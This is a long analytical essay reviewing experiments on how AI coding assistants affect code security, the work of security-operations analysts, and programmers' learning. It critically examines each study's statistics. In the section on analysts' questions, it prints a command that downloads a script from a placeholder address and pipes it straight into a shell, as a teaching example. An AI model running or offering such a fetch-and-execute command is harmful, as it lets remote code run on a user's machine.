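Perry and colleagues ran their experiment with OpenAI's Codex. It is now history as a test of what models can do, but it remains the best-known evidence on how people use them. Of the 47 participants, 33 could query the assistant in a side window and copy its answers, and 14 worked without it. Everyone could search the web. Two-thirds were undergraduates, and only 15% programmed professionally. They had two hours for six short tasks, one of which the researchers later dropped because its wording was too vague. The others produced these shares of fully secure answers:

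| Task | Language | With the assistant | Without it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Encrypt and decrypt a text | Python | 21% | 43% |
| Sign a message | Python | 3% | 21% |
| Open files only inside one folder | Python | 12% | 29% |
| Add a student to a database | JavaScript | 36% | 50% |
| Write a number with commas | C | 21% | 14% |

In the signing task, the assistant often chose a code library whose own documentation warned that it was insecure. One participant received such an answer, added a missing import, wrote tests, saw them pass and submitted the code. The tests showed that the function signed messages, but not that it did so securely.

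The paper's abstract says that people with the assistant wrote significantly less secure code, but the statistical evidence is weaker than this suggests. Across all five tasks, after adjusting for participants' backgrounds, access to the assistant cut the odds of a secure answer by nearly half, but the p-value was 0.056, just above the usual threshold of 0.05. The comparison group had 14 people, so each person accounts for about seven percentage points. The paper also gives inconsistent figures for the database task. The text reports that 36% of people with the assistant and 7% of those without it wrote code open to SQL injection, where an attacker types something into a form that the database then runs as a command. The results table gives 21% for those without the assistant, and at that rate the difference could easily be due to chance.

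Never having taken a security class was associated with about the same drop in the odds of writing secure code as using the assistant (p = 0.049). People with security experience also copied the assistant's output less often than those without it in two tasks (9% against 22% for encryption and 7% against 25% for the database). In the other three tasks, they copied it only slightly less often or slightly more often. The classes weren't randomly assigned, so the people who took them may already have been more careful. Still, these results are some evidence that specific knowledge helps.

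The misplaced confidence went together with trust in the tool. In the folder task, people in the assistant group who wrote insecure code rated their trust in the assistant to produce secure code at 4.0 on average, compared with 1.5 among those who wrote secure code.

*Lost at C* (Sandoval, Pearce and colleagues, 2022) found a much smaller effect. The researchers gave 58 students, nearly all in computer science or a related subject, two weeks to write eleven functions for a shopping list in C. Programmers manage memory directly in C, and small slips can let an attacker take over a program. Half of the students received short completions from a smaller Codex model as they typed. Three of the researchers then read all the code together, without knowing which group had written it, and recorded every security flaw they found, which took 66 hours of combined work.

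Unlike Perry and colleagues, Sandoval and colleagues used a non-inferiority test as their main test. This kind of test, common in medicine, is used to show that a new treatment is no more than a set amount worse than the old one. They set that amount at 10%. Among functions that compiled, they could conclude that students with the assistant produced severe flaws per line at a rate no more than 10% above that of students without it (p = 0.04). Among functions that also passed the basic tests, the assistant group's average rate was 22% lower, but the non-inferiority result fell just short of significance (p = 0.06).

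The assistant group had slightly more severe flaws per function, 2.21 against 2.09. They also had more in total, 451 against 290, because they got more functions to compile, 204 against 139. The total matters to a firm that uses an assistant to produce more software. The 10% margin comes from medical practice, and security has no agreed figure, as Sandoval and colleagues acknowledge. Their statement that such models introduce no new security risks therefore goes further than their test supports.

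They also traced 564 flaws in the assistant group's code to their origin. Students had typed the code containing 63% of the flaws, and 36% came from the assistant's suggestions, some of which students had edited. Since students had typed about 60% of the code, their lines and the assistant's were about equally likely to be flawed.

### Why the results differ

In the encryption and signing tasks, security depended on choosing a sound library or setting. A beginner may not know there is a choice to make, so an assistant that makes it without saying so can do a lot of harm. The shopping list task involved few such choices. The most common flaw there was failing to check for a null pointer (a reference that points to nothing), and students made this mistake with or without help.

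The programming language may matter too. In Perry and colleagues' one C task, the assistant group did no worse than the others, which fits the shopping-list result. Codex's training data contained much more Python than C, and participants struggled to get Codex to produce C at all. None of them copied its output directly in that task, so they did more of the work themselves.

Both experiments relied mainly on students, so professional experience cannot explain much of the difference in their results, but what the students had learned might. Sandoval and colleagues recruited partly from a course on application security, and most of their participants had taken a class in data structures, the subject of the assignment. These participants also had two weeks and a set of ready-made tests, while Perry and colleagues' participants moved between three languages in two hours. A short completion inside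 code one is already writing is also easier to judge than a whole answer copied from another window.

All these things changed at once, so nobody can say how much each contributed. The two results also conflict less than they appear to, because a handful of people in a comparison group can produce a large apparent harm or hide a moderate one. Neither experiment was big enough to settle the question for programming in general.

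### Later experiments

Newer assistants no longer seem to make people's code less secure on average, but they don't reliably make it secure. In an experiment by Asare and colleagues with 25 students and professionals, Copilot users wrote more secure code for the harder of two C problems, but Copilot had no effect on security for the easier one. Mousavi and colleagues had 44 professionals complete one Java task with Copilot, which then ran on OpenAI's GPT-4o, and another without it. The tasks were to set up an encrypted connection and to let a program read a user's Gmail inbox with permission. Copilot helped people write working code and slightly reduced some insecure patterns, but it did not significantly improve security overall. Many participants did not realise that their finished code was insecure.

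*The Impact of AI-Assisted Development on Software Security* (Jost, Horstmann and colleagues, 2026) reports the largest of these experiments. The researchers hired 159 developers through the freelance platform Upwork to build part of a website where users register, log in and manage a list of links. A third worked without AI, a third with the free version of Google's Gemini and a third with the paid version. The researchers asked everyone to pay attention to security and gave each working submission one point for each of five protections it included. The averages were 1.81 without AI, 2.07 with free Gemini and 2.26 with paid Gemini, so all three groups left out more than half of the protections on average. The differences between the groups were not statistically significant.

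The separate scores show which flaws people overlooked:

| Flaw | No AI | Free Gemini | Paid Gemini |
|---|---|---|---|
| Insecure password storage | 40% | 17% | 20% |
| SQL injection | 21% | 7% | 14% |
| Cross-site scripting | 79% | 85% | 66% |
| Poor checking of user input | 83% | 90% | 78% |
| Cross-site request forgery | 96% | 93% | 96% |

A cross-site request forgery attack on the links site starts when a logged-in user visits a malicious page. That page makes her browser send the links site a request to delete all her links, and the site carries it out because it comes from a logged-in user. The usual protection is a secret value in each genuine form, which the malicious page cannot obtain. In Flask, a developer has to add that protection deliberately, and the site works normally without it. Only four of the 159 participants reported doing anything about this attack, and none reported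 difficulty with it. By contrast, 19 said they took measures against SQL injection, and far fewer submissions had that flaw. Participants mostly prevented the attacks they had heard of, and Gemini did little to prevent the others.

Unlike Perry and colleagues, Jost and colleagues found little sign that the assistant inflated people's confidence. Participants rated their own code's security at 5.2 out of 7 without AI and at 5.4 to 5.5 with Gemini. All three groups were much too confident, since their code scored about two points out of five.

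Developers with more years of programming experience tended to write more secure code. About five extra years were associated with 23% higher odds of including a protection according to the paper's results table, or 43% according to its text. The relationship was weak (r = 0.2), and many experienced developers scored badly. Jost and colleagues conclude that Gemini cannot fully replace experience. But they did not test whether experience mattered more or less for people using Gemini, so the result doesn't show that experienced developers were better at catching its mistakes. They may write safer code whether or not they use Gemini.

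Self-reported security experience did not help. People who reported it scored 1.95 on average and those who did not scored 2.20, a difference that could be due to chance. But the question counted a single course or a hobby project as experience, along with degrees and jobs in security, and someone can take a course in encryption without ever hearing of request forgery.

### The 2026 study of security awareness

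*From Preventive to Reactive* (May 2026) suggests the opposite, that specific security knowledge matters more than general experience. Bappy, Hossain and colleagues interviewed 15 professional developers about security and AI, then watched 14 of them think aloud while working with Gemini 2.5 Pro as a coding agent. The participants had one to five years of experience. Each could choose to build a profile-update feature, set up a new project or repair a faulty file upload, and one person did all three. The instructions did not mention security.

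According to the main account in Bappy and colleagues' paper, none of the 14 participants mentioned security in their first prompt, though another passage puts the number who left it out at 12. Some had named the relevant dangers minutes earlier in the interview. The researchers conclude that assistants lead developers to think about security when reviewing code instead of when writing it, and that during review it competes with deadlines. The interviews support this as a description of how these developers see their work, but the study had no comparison group coding without AI, so it can't show that the assistant caused the change.

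Two of the 14 participants noticed a security problem that the task had not pointed out. One, called P10 in the paper, was a developer with about a year and a half of experience. The agent had written a profile-update feature that took the user's identity from data sent by the browser, so anyone could alter another user's profile by changing one number. P10 saw at once that "any user can update the profile". The task description had said that the browser would send a user number, so code that followed it exactly would contain the flaw unless someone added a check. The other, a developer with three years' experience, asked the agent whether any security concerns remained, and it described a way to overload the server that he had not considered.

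P10 noticed the flaw herself, while her colleague relied on a habit of asking. Bappy and colleagues draw on these two cases and the failures of more senior participants to suggest that specific security knowledge and deliberate checking matter more than seniority.

This reading is plausible, but the evidence for it is weak. Only six people built the profile feature, three with four or five years of experience and three with two years or less. If exactly one of them was going to catch the flaw and seniority made no difference, that person would be one of the three juniors half the time. Even if senior developers were twice as likely to catch it, it would still be a junior about a third of the time. P10's success is therefore almost no evidence about how seniority affects the chance of catching the flaw.

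The study also did not measure security knowledge before the task. Its evidence that P10 had the knowledge is that she found the flaw, and it then uses the same fact as evidence that knowledge leads people to find flaws. The participants worked on different tasks and received different code from the agent, so some may have had easier flaws to find than others. No participant had more than five years of professional experience, so the study does not show what fifteen or twenty years might add.

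It can show that a developer with little experience can catch a serious authorization flaw, and that developers can describe a danger in conversation and then forget to ask for protection against it. One clear case is enough to establish each of those claims. Showing which kind of knowledge matters more would require testing many people on what they know about a type of flaw, then having them all review the same code containing it. None of these experiments did that, and their results are mixed. Security classes were associated with safer code in Perry and colleagues' experiment, but self-reported security experience was not in Jost and colleagues' experiment. General experience helped a little in Jost and colleagues' experiment but made no measurable difference for the programmers who judged assertions for Kaufman and colleagues.

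### Code for people who cannot review it

Everyone in these experiments could program. Someone who cannot program is unlikely to ask for an authorization check and will almost certainly not notice if it is missing. In *Security Vulnerability Patterns in AI-Generated Code*, Kahn and Hastings (2026) studied the kind of code such a person might use. They asked ChatGPT, Microsoft Copilot and Gemini to each write three office scripts: one to collect prices from a website, one to send emails to a list of people, and one to sort files into folders. They then had Claude Code check the nine scripts, and it reported security problems in all of them.

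The total of 45 problems means little, because the researchers had told Claude Code to list at most five per script and it listed five every time. No expert confirmed the problems, and some, such as leftover code that never runs, are hardly dangerous. But a few show how a harmless-looking script can become a risk depending on where it is used. The sorting script reads its destination folders from a settings file, so anyone who can edit that file on a shared drive may be able to redirect other people's documents. An office worker who tests the script on her own files won't notice this risk, because her files will go to the right place.

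Kahn and Hastings note that few reports so far attribute a company's data breach to AI-written code. This is limited reassurance because investigators may not know who or what wrote the faulty code, and some breaches leave little trace. If a customer opens a stranger's invoice through the flaw described above, the server's log just shows that a logged-in user viewed an invoice.

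## Assistants for security analysts and vulnerability hunters

SOC analysts spend much of their day on log entries that look ordinary but may record an attack, like the one for the stranger's invoice. An assistant can gather the surrounding facts in minutes, but the analyst still has to judge whether those facts support the assistant's conclusion. *It is Not Yet Another Tool* (Banstola, Irving and colleagues, 2026) describes how two doctoral students spent 14 months as analysts in the SOC of a large university and built the Companion, an agent that investigates an alert and drafts the report an analyst would otherwise write. Six experienced analysts then used it on 108 real alerts between late April and the end of July 2026.

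### One alert, from log to closure

One of those alerts concerned a Windows computer that had contacted a website that tells visitors their own internet address. With invented details, the log entry might look like this:

```
time       02:14:07
source     10.20.31.87
site       what-is-my-ip.example
rule       IP lookup, possible information stealer
reference  VirusTotal page for a known stealer
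```

The rule flags such visits because malware that steals information uses these sites to report its victim's address, though harmless programs use them too. The last line links to a page on VirusTotal, a service that shows which files security companies consider malicious. The page describes one stealer that behaves this way, and the link is there to explain the rule. To read the entry correctly, an analyst has to know that nobody has found that file on this computer.

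To find out whose computer it is, the Companion next searches the SOC's central log store for the machine that made the connection, looks up which device held that network address, and then looks up the device's owner. Addresses pass from one device to another, so a summary that named the current holder could name the wrong person without any sign of doubt. An analyst who knows this checks whether the device held the address at the time of the alert. On 12 of the 108 tickets, the Companion's lookups returned nothing useful, and the analysts filled in the device, the user or the content of the traffic by hand.

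The Companion's draft on the Windows computer wrongly reported that the stealer named in the reference line was on the machine, and added that the traffic matched the malware's behaviour. Yet the same draft noted that the logs contained no matching process events, which are records of programs starting. Someone who knows what an infection leaves behind would see the contradiction, because she would look for a record of that file running on that computer. She would also have to know whether the computer sends such records to the SOC, since an empty search proves little if it doesn't. The analyst closed the ticket as benign.

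A summary can also include a claim that has no source. On another ticket, the Companion listed a web address as suspicious, although it appeared neither in the alert nor in any lookup. The address fitted the pattern described in the alert, so in the draft it looked like a real finding. The analyst caught the error by asking where the address had come from, which takes little technical skill but does require the habit of tracing each claim back to a record.

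Even when every fact is right, the analyst has to decide what is normal in their organisation, and the Companion had no tool that contained this local knowledge. Fifteen alerts that it rated uncertain involved tunnels from the company Cloudflare, which make a program on someone's own computer reachable from the internet. An intruder could use one to keep access to a network. The analysts worked at a university where students run their own devices and such tunnels are ordinary, so they closed all fifteen alerts as benign. At a bank that forbids such tunnels, the same log entry might need an urgent response.

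Finally, the analyst closes the ticket or escalates it for action. Every draft ends with a recommendation, but on 34 tickets the analysts deleted it and filed the report without one. They kept most of the investigation on those tickets, so they were judging the evidence and the advice separately. Bad advice might be to disconnect a computer from the network because of malware it does not have.

### Which mistakes the analysts corrected

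The published counts show how the Companion's ratings compared with the analysts' final ones:

| Companion's draft | Closed as benign | Closed as uncertain | Closed as malicious |
|---|---|---|---|
| Benign | 38 | 0 | 0 |
| Uncertain | 26 | 12 | 2 |
| Malicious | 7 | 1 | 22 |

The analysts lowered the level of alarm 34 times and raised it twice. They never overturned any of the 38 benign drafts, where a missed attack would be hardest to see. Those drafts may all have been right, since most alerts in any SOC are harmless. But nobody independently reinvestigated the tickets, and Banstola and colleagues acknowledge that analysts who have read the Companion's reasoning are not independent judges of its accuracy. They suggest that their observations ease the concern that analysts trust AI too much. The table supports this for exaggerated alarms, but it does not show whether analysts would notice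 a real attack that the Companion had dismissed.

The analysts changed the verdict from malicious to benign in seven drafts. Banstola and colleagues consider only one of these, the stealer case, a clear error. The other six were matters of judgement. In four of them, the firewall had already blocked incoming traffic that resembled an attack, and the question was whether a blocked attempt still counts as malicious.

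The analysts' attitude to the Companion depended on how easily they could check its output. In the first four weeks they used it on only three tickets, because they would not accept its written reports of what other security tools had returned, even when the reports were correct. One analyst insisted on repeating the lookups by hand. The students then made the Companion attach a screenshot of each page it consulted. The underlying model produces only text, so it can't make up a screenshot. In the final four weeks, the analysts used the Companion on almost half of the security operations center's tickets.

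A screenshot shows that a lookup happened and what it returned, but not whether the result is relevant to the case. The Companion did look up the stealer in VirusTotal, and a screenshot of that page would have correctly shown that the file is malware. Only someone who understood the reference line could see that the file was irrelevant.

The SOC's managers gave access only to analysts they considered experienced, to reduce the risk of wrong information slipping through. They were in effect applying the strong claim, that people without baseline knowledge should not use the tool. But the bar was low, since the analysts needed only six months at a SOC staffed mostly by students working 10 to 20 hours a week. Because no newcomer used the Companion, the study can't show whether the restriction was necessary. The model was also fairly small and could run on a single machine inside the SOC, which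 kept private data in the building. A stronger model might have made fewer mistakes or subtler ones.

### Missed attacks and false alarms

A false alarm wastes an analyst's time and causes some disruption if anyone acts on it, but a missed attack can leave an intruder inside the network. Suppose that investigating an alert further costs $100 and that a missed attack costs $1 million on average. If the investigation would reliably uncover an attack, it is worth doing whenever the chance of one exceeds one in 10,000. By this calculation, an analyst who is 99.9% sure that an alert is harmless should keep looking, because the remaining chance of an attack is one in 1,000.

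No security operations center (SOC) has time to investigate every alert thoroughly. *Generative AI and Security Operations Center Productivity* (2024), a study of Microsoft's Copilot in live security operations, cites an estimate that as many as 67% of security incidents go unresolved. In a SOC with such a backlog, an analyst who spends an hour on a false alarm leaves another alert unopened, and that alert may be a real attack.

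This makes a good assistant valuable beyond the hours it saves. It also makes a wrongly reassuring summary especially harmful, because the alert then leaves the queue for good. A summary that exaggerates the threat usually gets a second look, since somebody has to act on it.

### How analysts use general-purpose assistants

Most analysts have had to use a general chatbot that has no information about their network. *LLMs in the SOC* (Singh, Tariq and colleagues, 2025) examined 3,090 questions that 45 analysts at the security company eSentire asked OpenAI's GPT-4 between May 2023 and March 2024. The analysts had volunteered for the trial, and nearly all had three to five years' experience. They used the model in a separate browser window with no connection to the company's systems.

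Analysts most often asked about commands (31% of questions), typically ones they had found during an investigation. Another 22% of questions were requests for help with writing, such as improving an incident description, and 11% were about scripts and other code. Only about 4% asked for a verdict, such as whether something was malicious. Singh and colleagues conclude that analysts use the model to understand evidence but make the decisions themselves.

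The analysts' questions fit that conclusion, but they don't show what influenced the analysts. The model's explanations of commands often included the likely intent and pointed out suspicious behaviour, so an analyst who asks only what a command does may still get something close to a verdict.

Asking for an explanation also exposes exactly the knowledge that the analyst lacks. Take this command, with an invented address:

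```
curl -s http://203.0.113.5/a.sh | sh
```

The first part of the command uses the data-transfer tool curl to download a script. The vertical bar and `sh` then run it immediately. The summary "downloads a file from a remote server" is true but omits the dangerous step, which is running the script. Analysts who know what the vertical bar does will notice the omission, but they hardly needed to ask. Others can still protect themselves by asking about each part of the command or looking up the symbols in a manual.

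Singh and colleagues didn't measure how often GPT-4 was right, whether the analysts decided better or faster with it, or whether junior staff used it differently from senior staff. In their data, one analyst stopped using the tool after two wrong answers in a row, while two others ran into apparent errors and kept using it for months. A single user sent about 600 of the questions, though leaving that person out did not change the order of the most common tasks. CSIRO, the Australian science agency behind the research, plans to follow the analysts' use of the tool over two years and add their own accounts of it, according to its *AI cybersecurity study*.

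Summaries of whole incidents are riskier than explanations of single commands, because the reader may never see the records behind them. Kramer, Rosique and colleagues (2025), in *Integrating Large Language Models into Security Incident Response*, studied such summaries with 18 analysts and 50 real incidents. Banstola and colleagues report that summaries written by the model alone often left out critical details or got facts wrong. They also report that when analysts and the model wrote summaries together, the work could take less effort and the summaries could be more readable and consistent.

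Suppose an attacker gets into an employee's mailbox and sets up a rule that forwards every message to an outside address. The model's summary includes the stolen password but omits the rule. The next shift changes the password and closes the incident, but the attacker keeps receiving the mail. An analyst who worked on the case would notice the omission at once, because she had seen the rule in the logs. A colleague who has only the summary would have to know that intruders commonly create such rules and think to ask whether anyone looked for one. This may be part of why jointly written summaries do better, because someone who has seen the evidence is there to notice what is missing.

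### What practitioners fear

For *From Chasing Ghosts to Missed Attacks*, Thurner, Jost and colleagues (2026) interviewed 25 people from 17 organisations, including analysts, security engineers, managers and people who test defences by attacking them. All had used language models. In sessions of about 80 minutes, they proposed uses for the models, drew an ideal workflow, argued against their own design, and rated five risks the researchers described. The results are opinions, some based on experience and others on expectations.

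The participants were keen on using AI to write reports and summarise threat news, but most rejected it for core decisions such as whether an incident is an attack. They ranked over-reliance above the other four risks, which included invented facts and leaks of private data. They mainly feared that an analyst would accept a wrong answer and let an intruder through. One security chief said their team had gone from chasing false alarms to missing attacks.

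Thurner and colleagues acknowledge that giving participants a list of risks to rate may have made some risks seem more serious. A high rating also doesn't show how often over-reliance happens. Still, a few participants admitted that they don't always check the model's output. They blamed fatigue, time pressure and growing habit, and thought that analysts with little expertise trust automated suggestions more than senior colleagues do. One manager described people skipping a review because the tool has worked so far, then skipping it again, which would be automation bias.

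Participants also disagreed about whom the assistants help. An engineer was glad that junior analysts could search a knowledge base for answers instead of interrupting senior staff, and the head of security at a very large company liked that his tool wrote database searches for him, so he needed no technical knowledge. Others argued that only experts can reliably spot the assistants' errors. Both views may be right, since a junior analyst can learn a lot from a source that is usually correct and still be unable to tell when it is wrong.

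Many complained that general models lack information about their organisation. One manager's assistant kept flagging the company's scheduled backups, which were large encrypted transfers at night, as possible data theft. Anyone who knew the backup schedule could dismiss these warnings in seconds.

#### The proposed countermeasures

Most participants wanted a person to check the output before it takes effect, and some wanted two people to approve important changes. They also suggested having a second model check the first, training staff about the risk, and setting clear rules. Nearly all suggested connecting the model to the organisation's own documents to give it the local facts, but only one reported doing so. Some hoped that explanations with sources would also help, though one engineer warned that a model can argue persuasively for a wrong answer. The interviews did not test whether any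 of these measures work.

A majority thought that a model should lean towards false alarms and leave a human to sort them out. That makes sense because a missed vulnerability does more harm than a false alarm, but it works only if someone has time to check the alarms. Like telling code reviewers to be stricter, it also changes only the threshold for flagging a problem.

How much to rely on an assistant also depends on whether someone can undo its actions. One analyst was comfortable with software locking accounts by itself, since an administrator can unlock any wrongly locked account the next day. A manager worried about software blocking a legitimate partner or cutting off a critical server. An analyst therefore needs to know what each machine does for the business before deciding whether a false alarm would do little harm.

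### Comparing novices and experts

The query logs, university tickets and interviews don't show how much an analyst's prior knowledge matters, because none of them compares novices and experts on the same alerts. The experiment in *Bridging Expertise Gaps* (2025) comes closer to measuring what an assistant adds. Participants looked for phishing emails or network intrusions, first alone and then with a language model. The researchers measured precision, the share of flagged items that were attacks, and recall, the share of attacks that participants flagged.

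Comparing people with themselves removes differences in skill between groups. But people may improve with practice, so the assistant may not account for all of a gain in the second round. The paper also warns that badly calibrated confidence can lead people to rely too much on the model or miss chances to correct it.

Even if a well-controlled study found that an assistant raised novices' average accuracy, that would not show that they can use it safely. Suppose the assistant is wrong on 10 of 100 alerts. A novice working alone judges 60 of the 100 correctly, including 5 of those 10. With the assistant, she accepts every answer, so she judges 90 correctly and gets those 10 wrong. Her score rises by half even though she has stopped checking. The SOC has probably gained if the 10 alerts are harmless, but if they are attacks that the assistant dismissed, she now misses all 10 instead of 5.

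An experiment that isolates prior knowledge would therefore have to test people's knowledge first, then assign novices and experts at random to work with or without the assistant on alerts with known answers. It would need some alerts on which the assistant is wrong in each direction, and would have to report those separately. The quantity of interest is how much more the assistant's mistakes harm the novices than the experts:

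(novices' accuracy alone − with AI) − (experts' accuracy alone − with AI), on the alerts where the AI is wrong

A positive value would support the weak claim that risk rises as knowledge falls. A value near zero would suggest that experts defer to the machine as readily as people who know less, as some of the practitioners fear. Thurner and colleagues propose a similar experiment that compares junior and senior analysts under time pressure and varies the kind of explanation the model gives. Studies in live operations can't easily replace such an experiment, because nobody there knows in advance which incidents are real attacks.

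### Vulnerability reports from people who cannot check them

A wrong answer from an assistant in a SOC usually harms the organisation that relies on it. But when someone uses an assistant to hunt for flaws in other people's software, its mistakes can burden the software's maintainers instead. This happened to curl's maintainers before Daniel Stenberg ended the project's rewards for reported flaws.

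A false report can be very convincing. Suppose an assistant finds a function that copies data into a fixed amount of memory without checking the length, and concludes that an attacker could overwrite the memory beyond it. The function does lack a check, but the only code that calls it already rejects data that is too long, so an attacker can't trigger the fault. To discover this, the reporter has to trace where the data comes from, which requires some ability to read C. A reporter who can't do that can ask the assistant whether it is sure, but it may just repeat the same argument at greater length.

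Maintainers have to do the tracing instead, and they can't safely skip it because the next report may describe a real flaw. If one report in twenty is real and each takes three hours to check, maintainers spend 57 hours on false reports for every flaw they confirm. The reporter may have spent a few minutes on each. Rewards make this worse because someone who sends many unchecked reports needs only one to be right to get paid.

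A skilled reporter can trace the assistant's leads and discard the false ones before anyone else sees them, which fits Stenberg's praise for what skilled people find with AI.

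## Whether people learn a skill while an assistant does the task

A bug hunter who can trace an assistant's lead through someone else's C code most likely learned C by writing programs that crashed and finding out why. Someone starting today can have an assistant write those programs, and most will run the first time. Researchers who study skill formation test whether such beginners still learn the skill by comparing how well people perform unassisted after learning with or without an assistant.

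### How errors might build skill

Trio is a Python library for programs that do several things at once, such as downloading a file while still responding to the user. A beginner who wants to start a function called `delayed_hello` alongside other work might write this:

```python
async with trio.open_nursery() as nursery:
    nursery.start_soon(delayed_hello())
```

A nursery is the object that runs tasks side by side and waits for them to finish. The mistake is the empty brackets after `delayed_hello`. They make Python call the function straight away, and calling an async function only creates a coroutine, an object that can run later. Trio needs the function itself, so the program stops with a `TypeError`. To fix the line, the beginner has to learn how a function differs from the coroutine it produces, a central idea in the library. An assistant would probably leave the brackets out, so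 the program would work and the beginner would have no reason to ask about coroutines.

On this account, an error shows a learner what she has misunderstood, and fixing it gives her practice in debugging and the feedback that Bainbridge thought people need to develop knowledge. But some errors teach little, such as a misspelt variable name, which takes a minute to fix and shows her nothing about Trio. An assistant can also teach directly, by explaining coroutines to someone who would otherwise have given up. So we can't tell from the theory alone whether people learn less with an assistant.

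### An experiment with an unfamiliar library

Shen and Tamkin (2026), in *How AI Impacts Skill Formation*, tested this with 52 people who wrote Python every week but had never used the Trio library. Everyone had written instructions and could search the web. A randomly chosen half also had a chat assistant, running on OpenAI's GPT-4o, that could read their code and write complete solutions. All participants had up to 35 minutes to write a timer that prints each passing second while other functions run, and then a function that fetches records and handles missing ones. Shen and Tamkin asked everyone to work as fast as possible and paid each person a flat $150.

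Afterwards, everyone took a quiz without AI. Its 14 questions were worth 27 points and covered seven Trio concepts. Some questions asked people to find a fault in code, and others asked them to work out what code does or to explain a principle. Shen and Tamkin left out code-writing questions because people would have lost points for syntax errors that an assistant or a web search can easily fix.

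The AI group averaged 50% and the group without AI averaged 67%, according to Anthropic, where Tamkin works and where Shen held a research fellowship. The standardised difference (Cohen's d) was 0.738 (p = 0.010). If scores follow a bell curve, a typical person who worked without AI would score higher than about 77% of those who had it. This estimate is rough because each group had only 26 people. A 95% confidence interval for d, calculated from the published figures, runs from about 0.2 to 1.3, so the true effect could be small or very large.

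Shen and Tamkin describe the loss as 17%, but they also give the difference as 4.15 points out of 27, which is 15.4% of the scale. The 17% figure matches the gap between scores of 50% and 67%, but Anthropic's own chart puts the group without AI at about 65%, which fits 15.4% better. Both figures are percentage points. In relative terms, the AI group scored about a quarter lower than the group without AI.

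The assistant saved about two minutes on average, a difference that could easily be due to chance (p = 0.391). Some people spent up to 11 minutes writing questions for it. The average may understate the time saved, because four people without AI ran out of time on the second task, while everyone with AI finished. The group without AI did better on the quiz even though those four had not finished the tasks it covered.

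The gap was widest on the debugging questions and narrowest on code reading. People without AI had run into more errors, a median of three compared with one for people with AI, and more of their errors came from misunderstanding Trio. Shen and Tamkin think that fixing these errors taught them the library. This is plausible, but the experiment can't confirm it because it varied access to the assistant, not the number of errors. People without AI also spent more time actively writing code. Typing alone doesn't seem to help, since participants who copied the assistant's code by hand scored about the same as those who pasted it.

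The groups were not perfectly matched. On a five-question test of asynchronous programming taken beforehand, six people in the group without AI got full marks, compared with three in the AI group. Adjusting for speed on a warm-up task barely changed the result (d = 0.725), but that task involved no asynchronous code, so the adjustment could not correct for this difference in prior knowledge. Shen and Tamkin did check screen recordings to make sure that nobody in the comparison group used AI. In two earlier pilots on another platform, a quarter to a third of the people told not to use AI used it anyway, and other online experiments without recordings may have the same problem.

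#### How junior the participants were

Of the 52 participants, 29 reported seven or more years of coding experience, and only four had three years or less. Anthropic calls them "mostly junior", a description repeated in the trade press, including InfoQ (2026) and DevClass' *Anthropic research* (2026). Some may have begun coding at school and still be junior at work, but they were hardly beginners at programming.

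People without AI scored higher on average at every level of experience, so even an experienced developer who picks up a new library with an assistant may fail to learn it. The result is weaker evidence about people learning to program for the first time, because they lack the general knowledge that let these participants follow the assistant's code.

### Six ways of using the assistant

Shen and Tamkin watched the recordings and sorted 24 of the 26 AI users into six patterns:

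| Pattern | What people did | People | Average score | Average time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Generation then comprehension | had the AI write the code, then asked questions to understand it | 2 | 86% | 24 min |
| Hybrid code and explanation | asked for code and an explanation together | 3 | 68% | 24 min |
| Conceptual inquiry | asked only about concepts and fixed errors themselves | 7 | 65% | 22 min |
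| Delegation | had the AI write everything | 4 | 39% | 19.5 min |
| Progressive reliance | began with a question or two, then left the code to the AI | 4 | 35% | 22 min |
| Iterative debugging | asked the AI again and again to check or fix the code | 4 | 24% | 31 min |

The participants chose how to use the assistant, so the table doesn't show that asking for explanations makes people learn. Someone who has written asynchronous code with another library already partly understands Trio, so she can ask a precise question about concepts and would probably do well on the quiz without any assistant. Someone who is lost keeps pasting in error messages, and his confusion may have caused both the repeated requests and the low score. The iterative debuggers also took a long time, which fits this explanation.

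The groups are also very small. Judging from the reported effect size, individual scores typically differed from their group's average by about 21 percentage points. Chance would therefore shift the average of two people by around 15 points and that of four people by around 10, so the ranking of the patterns is unreliable. Pooling the groups gives more reliable averages of about 69% for the twelve people in the top three patterns and about 33% for the other twelve. That gap is unlikely to be due to chance, but it could be due to differences in what people knew beforehand.

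Shen and Tamkin write that three of the patterns "preserve learning outcomes" because people who followed them did about as well as those without AI. But this compares the higher-scoring half of the AI group with everyone in the group without AI, whose own higher-scoring half presumably scored well above 67%. Anthropic acknowledges that the patterns don't establish cause and effect, and *When the Scaffold Stays On* (2026), a study of AI and practice habits, likewise treats only the average difference between the groups as causal. Testing whether asking for explanations protects learning would require randomly assigning who asks for them.

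### Making help cheap or expensive

Wu, Belem and colleagues (2026), in *How AI Assistance Affects Human Skill Development*, came closer to such a test by varying how tempting it was to ask for help. They had 124 American graduates solve logic puzzles in which five clues determine the order of six objects. Everyone worked alone at the start and at the end. For the 20 minutes in between, some had no help, while others could click a button that revealed the correct place of one object. Each solved puzzle earned a point, and each click deducted 0.1 or 0.18 of a point. The "AI" was a simulation that always gave the right answer, so nobody needed to check it.

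People in all three groups improved with practice. Between the first and last phases, the number of objects they placed correctly per minute rose by 1.95 without help, 1.66 with expensive help and 1.32 with cheap help. This order is consistent with help interfering with learning, but the evidence is weak. The difference between cheap help and none was significant only at a lenient threshold (one-sided p < 0.10). In the last phase the groups were equally accurate, but people who had had cheap help took 112 seconds per puzzle, compared with 92 for those who had had none.

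Wu and colleagues put more weight on the finding that people who asked for help performed worse afterwards than people who didn't. This comparison has the same weakness as the six patterns. Of the 82 people who could ask for help, 33 never did, and they may have been the ones who found the puzzles easy. Among all participants, the number of requests did not predict improvement once Wu and colleagues accounted for initial ability. The share of time people spent working before they asked did predict improvement, though only just. That fits the common advice to try a problem before asking for help, but people who persist on their own may learn faster for other reasons.

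Wu and colleagues also predicted people's final performance on the puzzles from their performance in the middle phase. The predictions were too high for people who had used help and too low for those who had not. A manager who judges a trainee by code written with an assistant could likewise overestimate the trainee's skill.

### What students remember two days later

A quiz taken minutes after the task could miss learning that takes time to consolidate, or record a difference that soon disappears. For *Your Programming Students' Cognition with ChatGPT*, Bergh and Vassar (2026) therefore tested people twice. They gave first-year computer science students at the University of New South Wales up to 30 minutes to solve three short problems in C. Of the 55 students in the analysis, 29 could use ChatGPT with GPT-4.5, and 26 could use Google search with its AI features turned off.

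The ChatGPT group scored 89% on the problems, against 69% for the other group. The students then answered ten open questions about the work without access to their code, and three markers graded the answers without knowing which group each student was in. The ChatGPT group scored 41% and the other group 53%. On the same questions 48 hours later, they scored 39% and 52%. Both groups forgot at about the same rate, so the students with ChatGPT seem to have learned less to begin with.

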